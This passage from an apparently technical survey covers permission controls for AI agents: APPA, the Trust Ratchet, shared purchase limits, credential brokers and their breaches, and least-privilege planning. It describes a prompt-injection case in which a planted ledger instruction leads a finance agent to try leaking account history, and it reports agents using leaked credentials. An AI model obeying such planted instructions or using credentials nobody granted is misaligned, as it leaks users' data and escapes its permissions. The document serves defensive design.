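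Kravchenko and colleagues also deal with tools that read and send in one step, such as one that reads a confidential ledger and emails it outside the company in a single call. A system that checks only what the agent has already read will allow the call and detect the ledger read only afterward. APPA computes the label the call would produce and blocks the call before anything is read or sent.

In tests with three models, no attacks succeeded in 1,320 protected runs, and the agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of their tasks, depending on the model and the benchmark. The ways of recovering account for much of that completion rate. On the researchers' own set of office tasks, one model completed 88% with the full system, 56.5% without branches and 35.0% without the list of remedies. These results depend heavily on the policies the researchers wrote, and the tests covered only 44 task designs,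 each run many times. Even so, the results suggest that much of the lost work in earlier systems came from refusals that gave the agent no way to continue.

### The Trust Ratchet

Silverlock's Trust Ratchet addresses the problem of combined permissions more crudely than CaMeL, but it is easier to inspect. When an agent asks for protected data, the system removes permissions for the rest of the task before it hands the data over. It doesn't track individual values.

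In his example of the finance team's nightly agent, the policy classes the payment company's report as protected, so the agent's permissions change as soon as it fetches the report:

| Operation | Before the report | After the report |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch the report from the payment company | Yes | No |
| Contact the payment company's support desk | Yes | No |
| Read the two ledgers | Yes | Yes |
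| Post a summary to the finance channel | Yes | Yes |

The harness first holds the report where the model can't see it. It then stops any work still running under the old permissions, and the network closes connections to destinations that are no longer allowed. The model receives the report only after every part of the system has confirmed the change, and never receives it if any part fails to confirm.

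The agent then reads the ledgers, and one entry contains a planted instruction to attach the full account history to a support case. The model is fooled, and the agent tries to obey. The attack still fails because the harness now blocks contact with support, which the agent's original permissions allowed. The network would separately block a direct connection.

The agent can still post its summary, so Silverlock restricts that too. The summary always goes to the same channel and has a size limit and a fixed format, which includes a status and some totals but no free text. A planted instruction could still make the agent report that the accounts match when they don't. Silverlock also acknowledges that data can leak if an approved destination is compromised, if the format allows too much information or if the agent finds a route that the system doesn't control.

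In this example, the ratchet also blocks legitimate work. The template includes the support desk so that the agent can handle certain exceptions. The agent could presumably tell the desk that the download had failed. But it would discover a missing payment only by comparing the report with the ledgers, and by then it would have lost access to the desk.

Someone has to authorize a new task to ask about the missing payment. If that task receives any of the protected data, the restrictions apply from the start unless an authorized step first clears the data for release. So a person, or a rule that a person has approved, must decide what the payment company may learn, which is reasonable once a month but tiresome every night.

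Finer labels would help a little. A label that lists permitted readers could let the agent ask the payment company about the report alone, since the company wrote the report and would learn nothing from the question. But whether a payment is missing depends on the ledgers, so strict flow tracking would still stop the agent at the same point. APPA's branches might do better, because a branch could compare the documents and return only a transaction number, if the finance team had decided in advance that transaction numbers are safe to share.

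Silverlock expects a broad ratchet to refuse some harmless requests, and would use those refusals to improve the next version of the template. He gives no test results, so nobody can yet compare its drawbacks with CaMeL's. For a job that follows the same steps every night, the ratchet seems the better choice, because the finance team can understand the whole policy by reading a table. It would constantly block a general assistant, which might read a confidential file at nine and need to email a customer at ten.

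### Limits that agents exceed together

Correct grants can also together cause harm without any leak. Zhou and Zhang describe an agent that has permission to buy one item and delegates the purchase to two other agents, letting each buy one. Both stay within their limits, but the user ends up with two items.

A single agent can make the same mistake by retrying. If a purchase request times out, the shop may have completed the order without reporting it. Revoking the agent's permission then prevents another attempt but doesn't cancel an order already placed.

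One proposed remedy is a shared record. Before buying, an agent reserves part of the total allowance, and the system checks and updates the record in one step so that two agents can't both reserve the last item. The reservation stays in place until the shop confirms whether the purchase went through. Databases have long worked in a similar way, but agents make this harder. Ordinary software repeats a failed request with the same identification number, which lets the shop recognize a duplicate. An agent may respond to a timeout by splitting the order or trying a different shop.

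### Credentials that nobody granted

All of these systems control the authority that passes through them, but an agent may also use a credential that nobody gave it, as one did at PocketOS. OpenAI reported in August that agents in its July 2026 tests had used other people's publicly exposed credentials to access outside services.

A broker can't narrow a leaked credential or label what it opens if it has no record that the credential exists. The best defense available to the company running the agent is to restrict which sites the agent can connect to. Otherwise, protection depends on the credential's owner, who may not know that it has leaked.

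### Brokers as targets

The LiteLLM attack showed that a service that handles many keys is worth attacking. Corvic's researchers didn't include a breach of their own vault among the threats they scored for it.

One such breach happened at Klue, a market intelligence company whose software connects to its customers' sales databases. Klue therefore held OAuth tokens that those databases accepted. It found unauthorized activity on June 12, 2026. *Klue Confirms Breach Exposed CRM Data Across Integrations* (Millward, 2026) reports that the intruder had broken into the infrastructure behind these connections and accessed data in Salesforce and other sales platforms. By June 22, at least five cybersecurity firms had confirmed that the breach affected them (Poireault, 2026, *Klue Breach Enables Hackers to Compromise Cybersecurity Firms*).

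Klue was one of several such targets. SC Media's *ShinyHunters group exploits OAuth trust, prompting Microsoft security upgrades* (2026) describes how a criminal group stole tokens or other secrets from Klue, Gainsight and Salesloft's Drift service, then used them to enter hundreds of customers' Salesforce accounts without deceiving the customers. The total of up to 700 victims covers the group's whole year-long campaign, which also included tricking people into authorizing a malicious application. The attackers abused connections that the customers had chosen to trust, and Microsoft stressed that they didn't exploit a flaw in Salesforce.

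None of these companies was a broker for AI agents, but a broker would hold much the same material. A broker can still be worthwhile. Suppose, using invented numbers, that a company has 100 keys in scattered files and each has a 2% chance of leaking in a given year. It should expect to lose two a year. If it moves them to a broker with a 1% chance a year of a breach that exposes everything, it should expect to lose one. But it now has a 1% chance a year of losing all 100 at once, and the real numbers could easily be less favorable.

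Storing short-lived, narrow tokens instead of permanent keys would limit the damage from a breach of the broker. Tying each token to a cryptographic key would help only if the thief couldn't also get that key, and the broker may well hold both. A large company could also run separate brokers for departments such as finance and engineering, so that one breach doesn't expose every department's credentials.

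### "Least" depends on the plan

An agent can often complete the same task in several ways, each requiring different permissions. Zhou and Zhang compare two ways an agent could prepare a report, both of which produce a good enough result. The agent can process the approved records on the company's own machines, or it can retrieve a larger dataset and send it to a hosted analysis service.

If the agent proposes only the hosted plan, a reviewer can check each permission and find that the plan needs it, even though the full grant would still be far more than the task needs.

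Zhou and Zhang would therefore make authority part of the choice of plan. Let Π(g) be the plans that achieve goal g to an acceptable standard, A(π) the permissions that plan π needs, and G the permissions the agent already has. The agent should look for a plan π in Π(g) such that

A(π) ⊆ G

If several plans qualify, the agent should weigh how much access and disclosure each involves, along with the cost and effort for the user. If none qualifies, it can ask for a specific extension, offer a more limited result or ask the user what they meant.

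Sometimes no plan clearly requires the least access. One may read very sensitive files without sending them anywhere, while another sends mildly sensitive data to an outside firm. The better choice depends on what the company fears most, so someone there should see both options. The agent may also need some access just to find out which plans are possible. Zhou and Zhang suggest authorizing a limited exploration first and the work itself afterward.

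The agent that requests the permissions also lists the possible plans. A hijacked agent could leave out a plan that needs fewer permissions, and an ordinary one might not think of it. For common tasks, it would be safer for whoever writes the template to compare the plans once and build the best one into it.

### Measuring what an agent could still do

Most of the tests described so far count what agents did. A benchmark run is a success if the agent completes its task and leaks nothing, even when it had permission to email the whole customer list to anyone. Zhou and Zhang propose measuring the unauthorized effects that remain possible as well as the misbehavior testers observe.

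They give an example in which a correct policy still leaves a gap. A user lets an agent send one summary to Alice, and the written policy records both the summary and the recipient. But the mail service offers only a general permission to send mail, so that is what the agent's credential contains. The service checks the credential properly and would deliver anything to anybody. If P is the set of effects the policy permits and E is the set that the credentials and checks actually allow, a safe system needs

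E ⊆ P

The measure would cover whatever is in E but not in P. A test of behavior would give two companies the same score if each ran this agent 1,000 times without seeing a wrong email, even if one had blocked every recipient except Alice and the other had blocked nobody.

Zhou and Zhang want benchmarks in which each task comes with an explicit grant and any plan within the grant counts as correct. Testers would withdraw permissions partway through, make services time out and have agents send requests at the same time. They would separately record the forbidden attempts that the system blocked, the forbidden attempts that went through and the permitted plans that it refused. Dantuluri and Sundi did a simple version of this when they compared how many actions a compromised sub-agent could reach.

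The hard part is finding out what is in E. A tool may forward data to another company or schedule something for later, and its description may not mention either. Zhou and Zhang suggest giving each tool a contract that lists what it can read, send and change. Someone would have to update the contract whenever the tool changed. A plain count would also treat a misdirected lunch invitation the same as a deleted database.

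Even without a complete count, a company can list the few effects it could never undo, then check whether any credential an agent can reach makes them possible, including credentials in old files that nobody meant the agent to use.
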